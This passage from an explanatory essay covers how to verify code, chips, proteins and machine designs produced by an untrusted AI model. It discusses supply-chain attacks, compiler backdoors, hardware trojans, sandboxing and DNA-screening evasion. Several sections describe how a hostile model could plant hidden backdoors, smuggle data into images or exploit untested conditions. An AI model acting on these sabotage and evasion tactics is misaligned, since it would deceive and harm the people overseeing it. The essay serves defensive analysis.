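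In the same year, Andrew Dickson objected that a proof is about symbols, while the harms that worry people most happen in the physical world. Proving that a new DNA sequence is harmless, for example, would require a mathematical description of how it could affect human bodies and spread between people, and nobody has one that is accurate enough. A valid proof based on a poor description could give people false confidence.

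Supporters can reply that a safety rule need not always describe the harm. A DNA synthesis machine could be restricted to sequences on an approved list, and proving that its software obeys this rule requires no biology. But experts would still have to decide which sequences to approve, and researchers couldn't make a new sequence until someone approved it. A rule that limits the probability of harm avoids the need for certainty, but it is only as reliable as the model of the world used to calculate that probability.

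The two sides also differ about how easy it is to specify security. Tegmark and Omohundro think it is quite easy to specify that nobody can get into a computer without valid credentials. That specification may well be short, but it would not rule out a thief using a stolen password, or a program using the Meltdown processor flaw to read protected data without logging in as anyone else. A proof could still be useful for ruling out many common break-ins, as long as people did not mistake it for a guarantee against all of them.

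The case for proofs is strongest for software whose requirements concern only data and permitted actions. Examples include compilers, encryption software, programs that read complicated file formats, and systems that decide who may open a file. Specifications for such software can be much shorter than the programs themselves, and experts often agree on what to include. This software also benefits most as proofs become easier to produce, because finding the proof used to be the main obstacle.

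Dickson's objection is strongest for software whose harm depends on how people or living things respond, such as a program that gives medical advice or designs viruses. A proof can show that an advice program never reveals a patient's records, but nobody can write a formal condition that separates good advice from bad in every case. Software that controls machines, such as the boiler program in the first section, falls between these two cases, because engineers can describe a boiler much more accurately than anyone can describe a human body.

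Many programs contain both kinds of software, and developers can treat the parts differently. A hospital could require a proof for the part of its records system that decides who may see a file, and have doctors evaluate the part that suggests treatments. The proof protects the records only if the unverified part can't reach them without going through the verified part, so the hospital also has to control what the unverified part can do when it runs.

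## How should generated code be built and run?

Proofs rarely cover a whole program, so people who use generated code also have to limit what the unproved parts can do. Suppose a photo archive asks an untrusted model for an image converter that turns large scans into smaller PNG files for the archive's website. The model supplies source code, a list of other software the converter needs, and build instructions.

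The archive should first compute a hash of everything it received. A hash function such as SHA-256 turns a file of any size into a 256-bit number, and nobody knows a practical way to make two different files with the same number. If the archive records the hash before review starts and checks it again before building, it can be sure that it builds exactly the code its reviewers read. The University of Oxford's *Use Open-Source AI models safely*, a checklist for people who download AI models, recommends discarding any file whose hash doesn't match. It also warns against references such as "latest", which may later point to a different version.

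A hash protects against later changes to the code but not against faults already in it when it arrived. It is also little help if the archive copies the expected hash from the same web page as the file, because an attacker who can replace one can probably replace the other.

### Packages that do not exist

Most programs depend on packages, which are software that other people have published for reuse. A 300-line converter could easily rely on packages totaling 30,000 lines, so reviewers who read only the model's own code would miss most of what will run.

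Models sometimes name packages that don't exist. Anyone can publish on PyPI and npm, the main package registries for Python and JavaScript. An attacker can ask models for code, note which package names they invent, and publish malware under those names. Anyone who then installs everything a model lists may install the attacker's package. Seth Larson of the Python Software Foundation coined the name "slopsquatting" for this attack, according to *Bayesian-Calibrated Detection of Hallucinated Package Imports in AI-Assisted Code* (2026).

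Churilov (2026), in *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, gave five models about 40,000 programming questions each in April 2026, then checked the package names in their answers against the registries in November. Depending on the model, 3.6% to 5.0% of package mentions were of packages that didn't exist, and 2.2% to 3.4% of answers contained at least one. The five models had 104 invented names in common, so an attacker who registers one could reach users of several companies' models.

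In a 2024 test with the same questions, the average rate of invented names was 5.2% for commercial models and 21.7% for open ones. The open model in the newer test did about as well as the commercial ones, but the best rate has hardly changed. Stronger models have appeared since April, and an agent that looks up each name before using it may avoid the mistake. The rate depends heavily on the request. *Names Can Hurt* (Raj and Sahu, 2026) tested models that run on a user's own computer and found rates of 0 to 10% on routine tasks, but 40 to 73% on prompts designed to elicit invented names.

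Few people seem to have exploited this so far. Of the 2,282 invented names that Churilov followed, people registered 25 within about six months, and at least one of those packages contained malware. Researchers or defenders may have registered some of the others to keep attackers from using them. The models also suggested at least 23 names that had once belonged to malicious packages, which the registries later removed.

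A Python library's import name can differ from its name on PyPI. Programs import OpenCV, a popular image library, as `cv2`, but its PyPI name is `opencv-python`. Code that imports `cv2` is correct, but someone who tries to install a package called `cv2` will get whatever anyone has published under that name.

A short list of approved packages protects the archive better than a check that every package exists. That check would miss the dangerous case in which an attacker has already registered a name the model invented. A hostile model could also deliberately name a package that an accomplice had published, and anyone who noticed would probably think the model had made up the name by mistake. With an approved list, the archive has to reject or rewrite any code that needs other packages. It should also record the exact version and hash of each approved package.

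Approved packages can become dangerous too. On 4 August 2026, attackers took over the account of a maintainer of keyv, a popular npm package, and released a worm, malware that spreads by itself. *ChainDrop Worm Hits 400 npm Packages with Two Billion Monthly Installs* (Muncaster, 2026) reports that it reached more than 430 packages. The malicious versions of keyv and related packages carried valid provenance, a signed record of where and how a package was made. The record was accurate because the project's usual build system had made those versions from source code that the attackers had altered. Provenance can expose a package built elsewhere, but it is not evidence that the source code is safe.

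Users who had pinned their versions would not have received the worm automatically. Waiting a week before adopting any new release would also have avoided it, since security companies reported the attack within a day. A week's wait doesn't help against malware that stays hidden for months.

### Code that runs during the build

Even if the archive never starts the converter, building it can run hostile code. Many packages include install scripts, which a package manager can run as soon as it downloads them. Very few packages need these scripts, but *npms defaults are bad* (2026) explains that npm long ran them by default for every package, including the dependencies of other packages. An attacker exploited this after compromising axios, a widely used package. The attacker published a harmless package, added malware to it eighteen hours later, and made axios depend on it. Installing axios then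 gave the attacker remote access to the computer.

In July 2026 npm stopped running these scripts unless the user allows them, according to GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026). Malware can still run later, when someone uses the package. The Hacker News' *Malicious npm Package indexed-btree Hid Its Loader in Runtime Code Before Removal* (2026) describes a package that imitated a legitimate tool for keeping data in order. It had no install script, and its malware started when a program used the package to store an item. The malware then deleted its own files and the code that had started it. The package first appeared in June and had millions of recorded downloads before its removal.

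Build tools and code generators also run during a build. Endor Labs' *Trojanized @7nohe/openapi-react-query-codegen Adds PyPI to a Self-Replicating npm Worm* describes a compromised code generator that collected users' cloud credentials when they installed it. The XZ backdoor entered during compilation, and compiling a Lean proof can run its author's code.

The archive should therefore build the converter on a computer that holds no passwords, keys or other data worth stealing. It can download the approved packages, check their hashes, and disconnect the computer from the network before any build script runs. It can erase the computer after the build. Malware in a script would then have nothing to steal and no way to send anything out. But it could still alter the finished converter, which the archive has to move off the computer before anyone can use it.

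### What reproducible builds add

The archive can look for such tampering by having a second organisation build the converter separately and comparing the hashes of the two results. This requires a reproducible build, in which the same source always gives the same program, bit for bit. If the hashes match, an attacker would have had to corrupt both builds in exactly the same way. Many builds aren't reproducible because of harmless differences, such as a date that the build tool writes into the program.

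Some large projects now come close to full reproducibility. In May 2026, Debian, a free operating system based on Linux, began to block new packages that it can't reproduce, and existing ones that stop being reproducible, from entering the version under development (*bits from the release team*, 2026). Gevers (2026), who made the announcement, later said there would be exceptions. In the Reproducible Builds project's tests of the version under development, 95.4% of packages for the most common type of processor were reproducible and 3.3% were not. Most of the rest failed to build.

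Fedora's *Package builds are expected to be reproducible* says that about 90% of packages in another Linux system are reproducible, and sets a goal of at least 99% for Fedora. The June report from Reproducible Builds (2026) mentions a study that found 93% of the Nix package collection was reproducible in 2024, and says that IzzyOnDroid, a collection of Android apps, has reached two thirds. It also describes a demonstration in which a Debian computer checks each package with two independent rebuilders and installs it only if they confirm that they reproduced it.

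A matching hash shows that the builders produced the same program, but not that the program is safe. If the source contains a backdoor, or both builders use the same malicious package or compiler, they will produce the same malicious program.

### Thompson's compiler

Ken Thompson, a co-creator of Unix, used his Turing Award lecture, *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, to describe how a compiler could permanently hide a backdoor (Thompson, 1984). He built up the attack in three stages.

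1. He showed a program that prints an exact copy of its own source code. Such a program can carry any amount of extra material, which it copies along with the rest.
2. He explained how a compiler can know something that its source no longer contains. The C compiler is itself written in C. To teach it that `\v` means a vertical tab, a programmer first writes the character's code number, 11, into the source and compiles it. The programmer can then replace the 11 with `\v`, because the new compiler already knows what that means. The number now survives only in the compiled program.
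3. He changed the compiler so that, whenever it compiled the Unix login program, it added a password that he knew. He then made a second change. Whenever the compiler compiled its own source, it inserted both changes into the new compiler. After compiling this once, he could delete both changes from the source.

Anyone who then reads the source of the compiler or the login program finds nothing wrong. But compiling the clean compiler source with Thompson's compiler produces another compiler with the same backdoor. Independent builders who all start with that compiler will get matching results, so reproducible builds don't expose the backdoor. Thompson concluded, "You can't trust code that you did not totally create yourself."

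Thompson tried the attack on another group at Bell Labs. Accounts differ on whether anyone there noticed. *Trusting Trust*, a set of notes on the lecture, says someone did, because a mistake made the compiler one byte longer each time it compiled itself. Induc, a virus discovered in 2009, infected compilers for the Delphi language so that they infected every program they compiled. Skrimstad later demonstrated a self-copying attack on the compiler for Go, a modern programming language.

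A laboratory may also have to decide whether to trust a compiler that a model wrote. *Investigating an LLM generated C compiler* (2026) reports that Claude Opus 4.6, working with a team at Anthropic, wrote a C compiler that can compile the Linux kernel, and that writing it cost more than $20,000.

### Wheeler's test with a second compiler

Users can detect Thompson's attack with a method called diverse double-compiling. Henry Spencer suggested the idea in 1998, and *Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* (Wheeler, 2010) works it out in detail. Call the suspect compiler A and its source code s. The user also needs a second compiler, T, that can compile s. The test has three steps:

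1. Compile s with A. The result should be identical to A. If it isn't, the user has to find out why before going on, since the final comparison would also fail.
2. Compile s with T, and call the result B. The bytes of B will normally differ from those of A, because T translates programs differently. But B should do the same job as A, since both are supposed to come from s.
3. Compile s with B, and call the result C. If A really corresponds to s, then A and B turn the same input into the same output, so C will be identical to A.

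The user doesn't run A in the second or third step, so A can't affect C. If A contains a backdoor that isn't in s, the backdoor will be missing from C and the two files will differ.

The main assumption is that T doesn't insert the same hidden code when it compiles s. T can be slow or even malicious in other ways, as long as this doesn't affect the result. Wheeler recommends a T from unrelated developers, ideally one older than A, because its developers could hardly have prepared an attack on a compiler that didn't exist yet. If an untrusted model wrote the compiler being tested, T should therefore not be written by the same model.

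Accidental errors in T are less dangerous, because they usually cause a false alarm. If T translates part of s wrongly, B may behave differently from A, and C will fail to match. But frequent false alarms would make the test useless. Regehr (2026) cites tests in which the compiler written with Opus 4.6 mistranslated 14 of 101 random programs from one testing tool and 5 of 101 from another. That compiler would therefore be a poor choice for T.

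Wheeler's first demonstration produced a false alarm of this kind. He tested a small C compiler called tcc, using the GCC compiler as T, and the files didn't match. He traced the difference to a bug in how tcc handled certain numbers and to two bytes that it never set to a fixed value. After he worked around both problems, the files were identical. In *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* (2009), Wheeler added a formal proof of the method and applied it to GCC itself. He also used the method to detect an attack planted in a small compiler.

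The test shows only that A matches its source. If s contains a backdoor, A and C will too, so someone still has to review s. The archive can avoid most of this work by building the converter with an established compiler instead of one the model supplies.

### One file in and one file out

The archive should also keep the converter isolated during its first tests. The Oxford checklist recommends using test data, withholding real credentials, and storing logs where the software can't change them. The archive could convert several thousand scans and compare the results with those of a converter it already uses. The comparison should reveal most accidental mistakes, but not a backdoor whose trigger doesn't occur in those scans.

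When the converter goes into regular use, the archive can follow the principle of least privilege by giving it only the access it needs, which is to read one file and write another. Before any of the converter's code runs, a small, trusted launcher can open both files, pass them to the converter, and block everything else. Linux has a strict mode for this, in which a program can only read and write files that are already open, finish handling an interruption, and exit. The converter may also need to request memory, so the launcher would allow that up to a fixed limit. The launcher would also stop the converter if it ran for too long.

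The launcher has to impose these limits, because a hostile author could remove any that the program imposes on itself, as the XZ attacker did with Landlock. A backdoor in the converter then couldn't read the archive's donor records, delete its collection or contact anyone. But it could still misuse the two files:

- It could corrupt the image, for example by changing one digit in a scanned letter.
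- It could hide data in the image. A picture of 2,000 by 1,500 pixels has 9 million colour values, three for each pixel. Changing each by at most one step is invisible to the eye and can store 9 million bits, or about 1.1 megabytes.
- It could write a malformed file that exploits a bug in the program that opens it next.

The converter can only leak information that it has. It can't see the archive's passwords, but a scan might contain a donor's name or the place where a photograph was taken, and the converter could hide these details in a picture that the archive then publishes. If the archive starts a fresh copy of the converter for each scan and gives it nowhere to store anything, the converter can't carry information from one scan to the next. A trusted program can also remove private details before conversion and check afterwards that the output is a valid PNG file.

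Least privilege gives little protection against software that needs wide powers. An operating system update has to replace the programs that enforce other programs' permissions, so a backdoor in it can remove the limits. Dividing the update would still leave some part with dangerous powers, so users have to rely more on review, proofs and reproducible builds for such software. Backup software also needs wide powers, and it could steal data because it has to read every file and send copies elsewhere. But users can divide it into one part that reads and encrypts the files without network access, and another that sends the encrypted copies but can't read the originals.

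### Flaws in the sandbox

A sandbox is software, so it can have bugs. Some sandboxes are virtual machines, which imitate a whole computer, and others are containers, which separate programs that share one operating system. In 2015 researchers disclosed a flaw in the virtual floppy disk drive of several widely used virtual machine systems. In 2019 other researchers disclosed a flaw in runc, which starts containers for Docker and similar tools. Until users installed the fixes, a malicious program could have used these flaws to affect the computer outside its sandbox. Processor flaws such as Meltdown can also weaken the separation between programs, even if the sandbox software has no bugs.

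People can also set up a sandbox wrongly. In tests in 2026, for example, AI models entered outside companies' systems through an internet connection that should not have been there.

Tight permissions make bugs harder to exploit. A converter that can only read, write and request memory can reach far less of the operating system's code than a game that uses graphics, sound and the network. For important builds, the archive can also use a separate physical computer. For diverse double-compiling, Wheeler recommends a separate computer with no outside connection and no unnecessary programs, because even a program without special permissions might exploit an unknown flaw to interfere with the compiler.

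### Releasing in stages and going back

The archive can use the converter for a small share of its scans at first, to limit the harm from anything it has missed. If an accidental fault spoils one picture in 1,000, the first 5,000 pictures will almost certainly include a spoiled one. Staff should inspect these early results more closely than later ones so that they notice it.

A staged release gives little protection against a backdoor that activates only after everyone has the program. Wheeler describes an employee of the financial company UBS PaineWebber who planted a few lines of code that checked the date. On 4 March 2002, after he had resigned, the code made more than 1,000 of the company's computers start deleting files. Installing the code on ten computers first would have revealed the problem only if someone had set those computers' clocks forward.

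The archive also needs a way to return to its old converter, and the Oxford checklist advises planning this before the software goes live. The archive should keep the old converter and the original scans, and record the hash of the converter that made each picture, so that if it later finds a fault, it knows which pictures to make again. It can't take back data hidden in pictures that people have already downloaded. Stolen credentials can also still be used after the program is removed, which is why the security company Wiz told victims of the ChainDrop worm to replace theirs and rebuild affected computers.

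A bad operating system update is harder to undo, because it may have altered the tool that would undo it. Users should keep a copy of the old system on a disk that the update can't write to, and check that the computer can start from that copy before installing the update.

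## How are designs for chips, proteins and machines checked?

People can test a program in the exact form they will use, but a design for a chip, a protein or a machine only describes an object that somebody still has to make. A specification for such a design applies only to a simplified mathematical model of the world, so the last test is to measure the finished object.

Suppose that an AI model designs a steel arm, fixed to a wall at one end, that has to carry a load at the other. If F is the load and the arm has length L, width b and thickness h, the greatest stress in the steel is

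6FL / (bh²)

For a load of 2,000 newtons (the weight of about 200 kilograms) and an arm 200 mm long, 30 mm wide and 20 mm thick, the stress is 200 megapascals. Ordinary structural steel starts to bend permanently at about 250 megapascals, so the design passes. Anyone can repeat the calculation without trusting the designer. But if the workshop makes the arm only 17 mm thick, the stress rises to 277 megapascals and the arm bends permanently.

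Engineers therefore build an arm and load it. Loading it once would reveal weak steel, but not the slow cracking that millions of smaller loads can cause. A hostile designer could exploit such gaps, for example by choosing dimensions that make a rotating part shake violently at one speed the usual tests skip.

Physical safeguards can limit the damage from a bad design, as a sandbox does for software. A relief valve lets steam out of a boiler at a set pressure, whatever the boiler's designer intended. The untrusted model should not design the valve.

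### Proving that two circuits do the same thing

Digital chips are easier to check in advance, because their designers can describe them almost entirely in zeros and ones. A chip consists of gates, tiny circuits that combine these values. An AND gate outputs 1 if both its inputs are 1, and an OR gate outputs 1 if at least one is.

Equivalence checking proves that two circuits give the same output for every input. Suppose that a circuit feeds inputs a and b into an OR gate, then feeds the result and a into an AND gate. A model proposes to remove both gates and use a itself as the output. With two inputs, there are only four cases:

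| a | b | a OR b | a AND (a OR b) |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| 0 | 1 | 1 | 0 |
| 1 | 0 | 1 | 1 |
| 1 | 1 | 1 | 1 |

The last column always equals a, so the two gates did nothing useful and the change is safe.

A table becomes too long for real circuits. A circuit that adds two 64-bit numbers has 2^128 possible inputs, or about 3.4 × 10^38. Engineers instead connect the outputs of the two circuits to an extra gate that outputs 1 only when they differ. They then use a program called a solver to find an input that produces a 1, or to prove that none exists. The solver can rule out many inputs at once. In the example, if a is 0, the AND gate outputs 0 whatever b is. If a is 1, the OR gate outputs 1, so the AND gate does too. Solvers can check many large circuits this way, but some, especially multipliers, can take far too long.

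The trusted circuit serves as the specification, so nobody has to write a separate one. Any mistake or backdoor in the trusted circuit will also be in the new circuit.

Chip designers already use circuits that AI has improved. Google DeepMind's *AlphaEvolve* (2025) describes an agent in which Gemini models propose programs and automatic tests select the best. The agent rewrote part of an arithmetic circuit in Google's Tensor Processing Unit (TPU), a chip for AI calculations, to remove unnecessary bits. Google DeepMind required the new version to pass "robust verification methods" to confirm that it still worked, but did not name them. The TPU's designers also validated the change, and Google's ordinary design software later found the same simplification independently. The improvement was therefore modest, but engineers could accept it without trusting the agent.

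NVIDIA's Hopper chips contain nearly 13,000 instances of other AI-designed circuits, according to ALLPCB, an electronics website. One design, for adding 64-bit numbers, was 25% smaller than a comparable circuit from leading design software.

Equivalence checking is harder to apply when a model designs a new circuit, because there may be no trusted circuit to compare it with. *Veritas* (2025) compared its model's adders, subtractors and multiplexers (circuits that select one of several inputs) with trusted versions, and all of them matched. But these circuits were small. Two 4-bit numbers have only 256 combinations, so a table of the correct outputs would have been enough to check against.

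Researchers often rely on tests alone to check circuits. In *Verilog-Evolve* (2026), AI-written circuits passed the public tests for 85.3% of the problems in one collection and 72.8% in another. Passing these tests is good evidence that a circuit has no common mistakes, but as with software, tests can miss a fault that only a rare input triggers.

### Hardware trojans

A hardware trojan is a malicious change to a chip, often activated by a trigger. *Quantum Trojan Insertion* (2025) notes that triggers range from rare inputs to conditions in the chip's surroundings. For example, a trojan could reveal an encryption key after the chip has performed a billion operations.

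An untrusted model can insert a trojan while it designs a chip, but people can also insert one later. *Hardware Trojans from Invisible Inversions* (2026) explains that most companies that design chips no longer own advanced factories. They send a digital layout to another company's factory, where a dishonest engineer could change it, or someone could alter the files on the way. Designers also depend on suppliers for standard cells, which are ready-made gates and other small circuits. In *An Automated Framework for Generating Stealthy Cell-Embedded Hardware Trojans* (2026), the attacker is a supplier who hides a trojan inside a cell that otherwise works normally.

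| When the change enters | Who could make it | What an equivalence check would reveal |
|---|---|---|
| Rewriting a trusted circuit | The model | Any difference in the outputs |
| Designing a new circuit | The model | Nothing, unless someone else supplies a trusted version |
| Adding standard cells | The supplier | Nothing, if the check uses the supplier's own description of the cells |
| Making the chip | The factory, or someone who intercepts the files | Nothing, because the check compares designs and not finished chips |
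| Delivery and repair | Anyone who handles the chip | Nothing, for the same reason |

Even for a rewritten circuit, the check covers only the outputs. Two equivalent circuits can use different amounts of power, and an observer who measures the power use may be able to work out a secret key.

Engineers can look for later changes by comparing a finished chip's power use, delays or electromagnetic emissions with those of a trusted chip. *SenTrojan* (2026), which studies trojans in sensors, points out that no trusted reference exists if the same party controls both the altered design and the reference. A laboratory checking a model's design should therefore not accept a reference circuit from that model.

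Automatic trojan detectors are not yet a good substitute. In *Automated Hardware Trojan Insertion in Industrial-Scale Designs*, Popryho, Pal and Partin-Vaisband (2025) note that real chips often have hundreds of thousands to millions of internal connections, far more than public test cases. They built large test cases by adding harmless patterns that resemble trojans. Leading machine-learning detectors failed to find these patterns.

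A model that only writes design files can't change anything at the factory, so the risk of tampering there is much the same as for a chip that people designed. The extra risk is in the design itself. Engineers can reduce it by asking the model to modify circuits they already trust.

### What a binding test shows

Protein designers have nothing like an equivalence check. A protein is a chain of smaller molecules called amino acids, and it folds into a shape that largely determines what it does. Software can predict the shape, but nobody can prove that the protein will work in a living body.

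OpenAI's *GPT-6 models demonstrate intrinsic protein-design capabilities* (24 November 2026) describes how the company's models design proteins by reasoning and writing code. GPT-6.2 received the three-dimensional structures of five target proteins and designed small proteins to bind to them. Specialised models then supplied the amino-acid sequences and chose which designs to test, as 凤凰网's *OpenAI称GPT-6可独立设计蛋白质结构，实验成功率仍落后于专用模型* (2026) reports.

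The company Onava made and tested 322 of the designs, and 35 of them (10.9%) bound their targets. The original paper on RFdiffusion, a specialised design tool, reported 19%, although the two studies used partly different targets.

The average combines targets with very different success rates. oaoage's *OpenAI、GPT-6 でタンパク質の設計。結合を試した35件が狙いの標的に結合* (2026) lists 18 successful designs for one target, IL-17A, and only one for another, TrkA. If Onava tested about 64 designs for each, the success rates were about 28% and 1.6%. At those rates, a user who tested 20 designs would almost certainly find at least one that binds to a target like IL-17A, but would have only about a 27% chance with a target like TrkA.

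Starting from proteins that already work gives better results. In a second experiment, the models redesigned the binding parts of six nanobodies, which are small relatives of antibodies, and 128 of the 182 new versions bound.

In most of the computer evaluations, OpenAI's strongest model was an internal one it had not released. Outsiders who receive designs from such a model should be cautious about computer-generated scores. OpenAI wrote about an earlier protein model that computer evaluations are "often of limited value" because it is unclear whether better scores lead to more useful proteins.

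A binding test usually measures how much of a protein sticks to its target at different concentrations. In the simplest case, if c is the concentration of the free protein, the fraction of targets it occupies is

c / (c + K)

where K is the concentration at which it occupies half of them. A protein with K = 10, used at a concentration of 100 in the same units, occupies about 91% of its targets.

A test with the target alone does not show what else the protein binds. Suppose that it also binds another protein in the body, 100 times more weakly, so that K = 1,000. It then occupies only about 9% of that protein's molecules. But if those molecules are 100 times as common as the target, ten times as much of the drug binds to them as to the target.

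A protein that binds to its target might block it, activate it or have no effect, depending on where it attaches. Even after confirming binding, researchers still have to find out whether the protein is stable and has the intended effect in cells, and whether it is toxic or provokes an immune reaction.

Even animal tests can miss severe effects. In 2006, six healthy volunteers in London became critically ill within hours of receiving an antibody called TGN1412. The antibody bound its intended protein, and the dose was one five-hundredth of the amount that had appeared safe in animals.

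### Proteins that are dangerous because they work

Testing shows a malicious user which versions of a toxin work. *Protein design, generative AI and biological security* notes that designed proteins that bind to viruses could become treatments, but the same design methods could produce new toxins.

Someone who designs a protein on a computer usually needs DNA that encodes it. Microsoft's *The Paraphrase Project* explains that a researcher can order this DNA from a synthesis company and receive a vial within days. The company can first screen the order with software that checks whether the sequence resembles known toxins or parts of dangerous microbes. It can also check who the customer is, but *Beyond sequence similarity* says this can't replace screening the sequence.

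Screening works well on ordinary sequences. *Inter-tool analysis of a NIST dataset* reports that when NIST gave software developers unlabeled test sequences, every tool identified more than 95% of the dangerous ones. AI-designed proteins are harder to screen because they can have an unfamiliar sequence but a shape similar to that of a dangerous protein. Microsoft compares this to paraphrasing a sentence, which changes the words but keeps the meaning.

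In *Strengthening nucleic acid biosecurity screening against generative protein design tools*, Wittmann, Alexanian and colleagues (2025) used publicly available AI tools to redesign 72 proteins of concern (the number is from AIChE's *AI-Designed Proteins Expose Gaps in Biosecurity*, 2025) and submitted the results to four screening tools. The screening tools flagged nearly all the original proteins but missed many of the redesigned ones. One missed more than three quarters of the potential toxins.

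Jacob Beal's team makes one of the tools. He recalls in The Tech's *Preventing the next bioweapon* (2025) that when he first tested it on 10,000 altered versions of a toxin, it caught almost none of them. The researchers kept the problem secret while they worked with the tools' developers to fix it. This took ten months, according to Microsoft's *Researchers find — and help fix — a hidden biosecurity threat*.

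After the fix, the tools detected an average of 97% of the redesigned proteins that computer measures rated as more likely to keep their function. The researchers never made the proteins, so nobody knows how many of the 3% that the tools missed would have worked. James Diggans of the DNA synthesis company Twist Bioscience says in Science News' *AI-designed proteins test biosecurity safeguards* that "close to zero" people have tried to produce malicious proteins.

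Later laboratory work was somewhat reassuring. In *Experimental Evaluation of AI-Driven Protein Design Risks Using Safe Biological Proxies*, Ikonomova, Wittmann and colleagues (2025) made and tested redesigned versions of harmless proteins. A predicted shape close to the original did not guarantee that a redesigned protein kept its activity. They concluded that current tools could not reliably disguise a protein from screening while preserving its activity. Testing the designs also took considerable time, skill and money, which would slow an attacker.

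This reassurance may not last, and may not extend to the strongest private models. Wittmann, Wheeler and colleagues (2026), in *The limits of sequence-based biosecurity screening tools*, judge that the improved software works against widely used design tools. But it would fail if a future tool could design working proteins that barely resemble natural ones. Screening would then have to predict what a protein does, and no system that can do this is ready for use. So if a laboratory's unreleased model designs proteins better than public tools do, the laboratory can't assume that DNA companies would catch a dangerous design.

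Screening also remains voluntary in many places. *Synthetic nucleic acids in a post-agent biosecurity Era* reports that the UK, the US, New Zealand and the EU have put forward guidance or legislation.

Checks can also take place earlier. NTI's *Risky Business* describes a method for screening requests to protein-design tools. A laboratory can screen the requests its model receives and have biosecurity experts examine any worrying design before release. It can also restrict who receives sensitive details, as Wittmann and colleagues did with their data. Other researchers can obtain that data only by applying to an international biosecurity organisation.

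### What a test and a mistake cost

How much evidence people should demand before they build something depends on what a physical test costs and whether a mistake can be undone. The figures below are rough, because a chip for a toy and a chip for a data centre have very different costs.

| | Chip | Protein medicine | Machine |
|---|---|---|---|
| Check before making it | Equivalence check, if a trusted circuit exists | Predicted shape, which is weak evidence | Calculation of stresses and movement |
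| Cost of physical tests | Often millions of dollars for a first batch of advanced chips | Fairly low for a binding test, many millions for trials in people | From a few dollars for a simple part to millions for an engine |
| Time to a result | Usually months for the first chips | Days to weeks for binding, years for safety | Minutes to load a simple part, months or years to study wear |
| Undoing a mistake | New software can sometimes work around the fault, otherwise owners must replace the chip | Doctors can stop the treatment, but may not be able to reverse its effects | Owners can repair or replace the machine, but can't undo injuries |

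A company should check a chip design as thoroughly as possible before manufacturing it, because the strongest check happens at that stage and a mistake in the finished chip is expensive. For example, nobody could rewire the processors that had the Meltdown flaw.

Protein designers are in nearly the opposite position. Their computer checks are weak and the first laboratory tests are fairly cheap, so they can reasonably make many harmless candidates and discard those that fail. They must be much more careful once people receive the protein. A design that can spread by itself, such as a virus, is the worst case because nobody can recall it.

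### Accepting a design that nobody understands

Sometimes a design performs well in tests, but no engineer can explain why. In Google DeepMind's *AlphaEvolve* (2026), the company's chief scientist Jeff Dean calls one of the agent's circuits "so counterintuitive yet efficient" that Google built it into its next TPUs. He does not say that engineers failed to understand it, but more capable models may well produce designs that nobody can follow.

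People who would accept such designs based on test results can point to a good record in medicine and engineering. Doctors used aspirin for about 70 years before John Vane explained in 1971 how it reduces pain. In 2006 NASA launched an antenna whose odd, bent shape came from a program that imitates evolution. Engineers could measure its signal without knowing why each bend helped. Insisting on an explanation would have delayed useful products, and a convincing explanation can still be wrong.

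Others reply that tests cover only the conditions someone thought of trying, and that understanding a design helps engineers choose which conditions to test. In 1996 Adrian Thompson of the University of Sussex used simulated evolution to produce a circuit that could distinguish two tones. The circuit depended on physical quirks of the part of the chip where it had evolved, and it performed worse when he moved it elsewhere on the same chip. Understanding also helps people repair a design. Google DeepMind said in 2025 that one advantage of the code AlphaEvolve produced for managing Google's data centres was that people could read, predict and debug it.

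The examples from medicine and engineering also had no hostile designer. Nobody designed aspirin to pass a trial and then harm patients years later. An untrusted model might produce a design like that, and it may have exact information about which tests the design will face.

Engineers can rely largely on an equivalence proof to check an arithmetic circuit. The proof covers every input, so they don't need to know how the model found the circuit, but they still have to measure its speed and power use. Test results may be enough for a simple machine part if people can test it in all the conditions it will meet and a failure would do little harm.

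Test results alone are much less convincing for a chip that controls a car's brakes, where one rare input could kill someone. The manufacturer could reject the unexplained design and use a larger or slower one that its engineers understand. Medical researchers often lack that option, because they can't fully predict the effects of any new protein, even one that a person designed. They can start with very small doses, treat one volunteer at a time, and have people with no stake in the design decide whether to continue.

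## Is releasing only the output safer than giving access to the model?

A laboratory can share a powerful model in four main ways. It can publish the weights, so anyone with suitable computers can run the model. It can let the public query the model through an app or a programming interface. It can limit that access to selected partners, such as companies that maintain critical software. Or it can release only the artifacts the model produces, such as code, proofs and designs, so nobody outside the laboratory can query the model.

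Artifact-only release is the safest of these options for some kinds of work. For others, it protects people much less than it seems to, because a released program can be as dangerous as the model that wrote it and the model can still do harm inside the laboratory.

### Structured access

Public access and partner access can both be forms of structured access, which *Structured Access* (Shevlane, 2022) describes as a controlled interaction between an AI system and its user. The developer decides who may use the system and for what. For example, a company that doesn't want its model to diagnose illnesses could turn away customers who plan to use it for that. The developer also has to stop users from altering the model or building their own version of it. Otherwise these limits achieve little, since someone who has the weights can retrain the model until it no longer refuses anything.

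Shevlane's argument depends on a model being both information and a tool. A developer can let people use the tool without giving them the information they would need to copy it. The developer can then watch how people use the model, ban those who misuse it, and withdraw an ability that turns out to be harmful. The developer can do none of this after publishing the information, because people can pass it on and nobody can take it back.

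Publishing only part of the information doesn't solve the problem. Microsoft researchers worried that their chatbot, DialoGPT, would produce offensive text, so they published the model without the last piece of code needed to generate text. Users who found replacement code online had full use of the model, and the rest could generate no text.

Shevlane's reasoning about models also applies to artifacts, and it partly counts against artifact-only release. Once a laboratory has published a program, it can't see who runs the program or stop them, whereas it can do both if it lends its model to partners. Artifact-only release is therefore safer than structured access only if people can do less harm with the artifacts than they could with supervised use of the model.

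Some services combine the two approaches. Anthropic's *Bringing the cybersecurity capabilities of Claude Mythos 5 to more defenders* (2026) explains how business customers can use the company's strongest cybersecurity model to scan their code. They receive a list of flaws and suggested patches (small changes that repair a program) but can't ask the model to write an attack. Anthropic argues that the riskiest behaviour occurs when a malicious user can steer a model directly, and that the risk is much lower if users receive only specific outputs.

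Customers still have a little control over the model, because they choose which program it scans. Someone could submit a copy of another organisation's program to learn its flaws. Anthropic intends the service for code that customers own, and it has measures to prevent abuse of the partner products that use the same model.

### Four arrangements compared

In this table, "sabotage" means deliberate harm by the model itself, and "dangerous content" means output that is harmful because it works.

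| | Open weights | Public access | Selected partners | Artifacts only |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Misuse by outsiders | Anyone can remove the safeguards | The laboratory can refuse requests and ban users, but will miss some | Fewer users, whose identity the laboratory knows | Limited to what the artifacts make possible |
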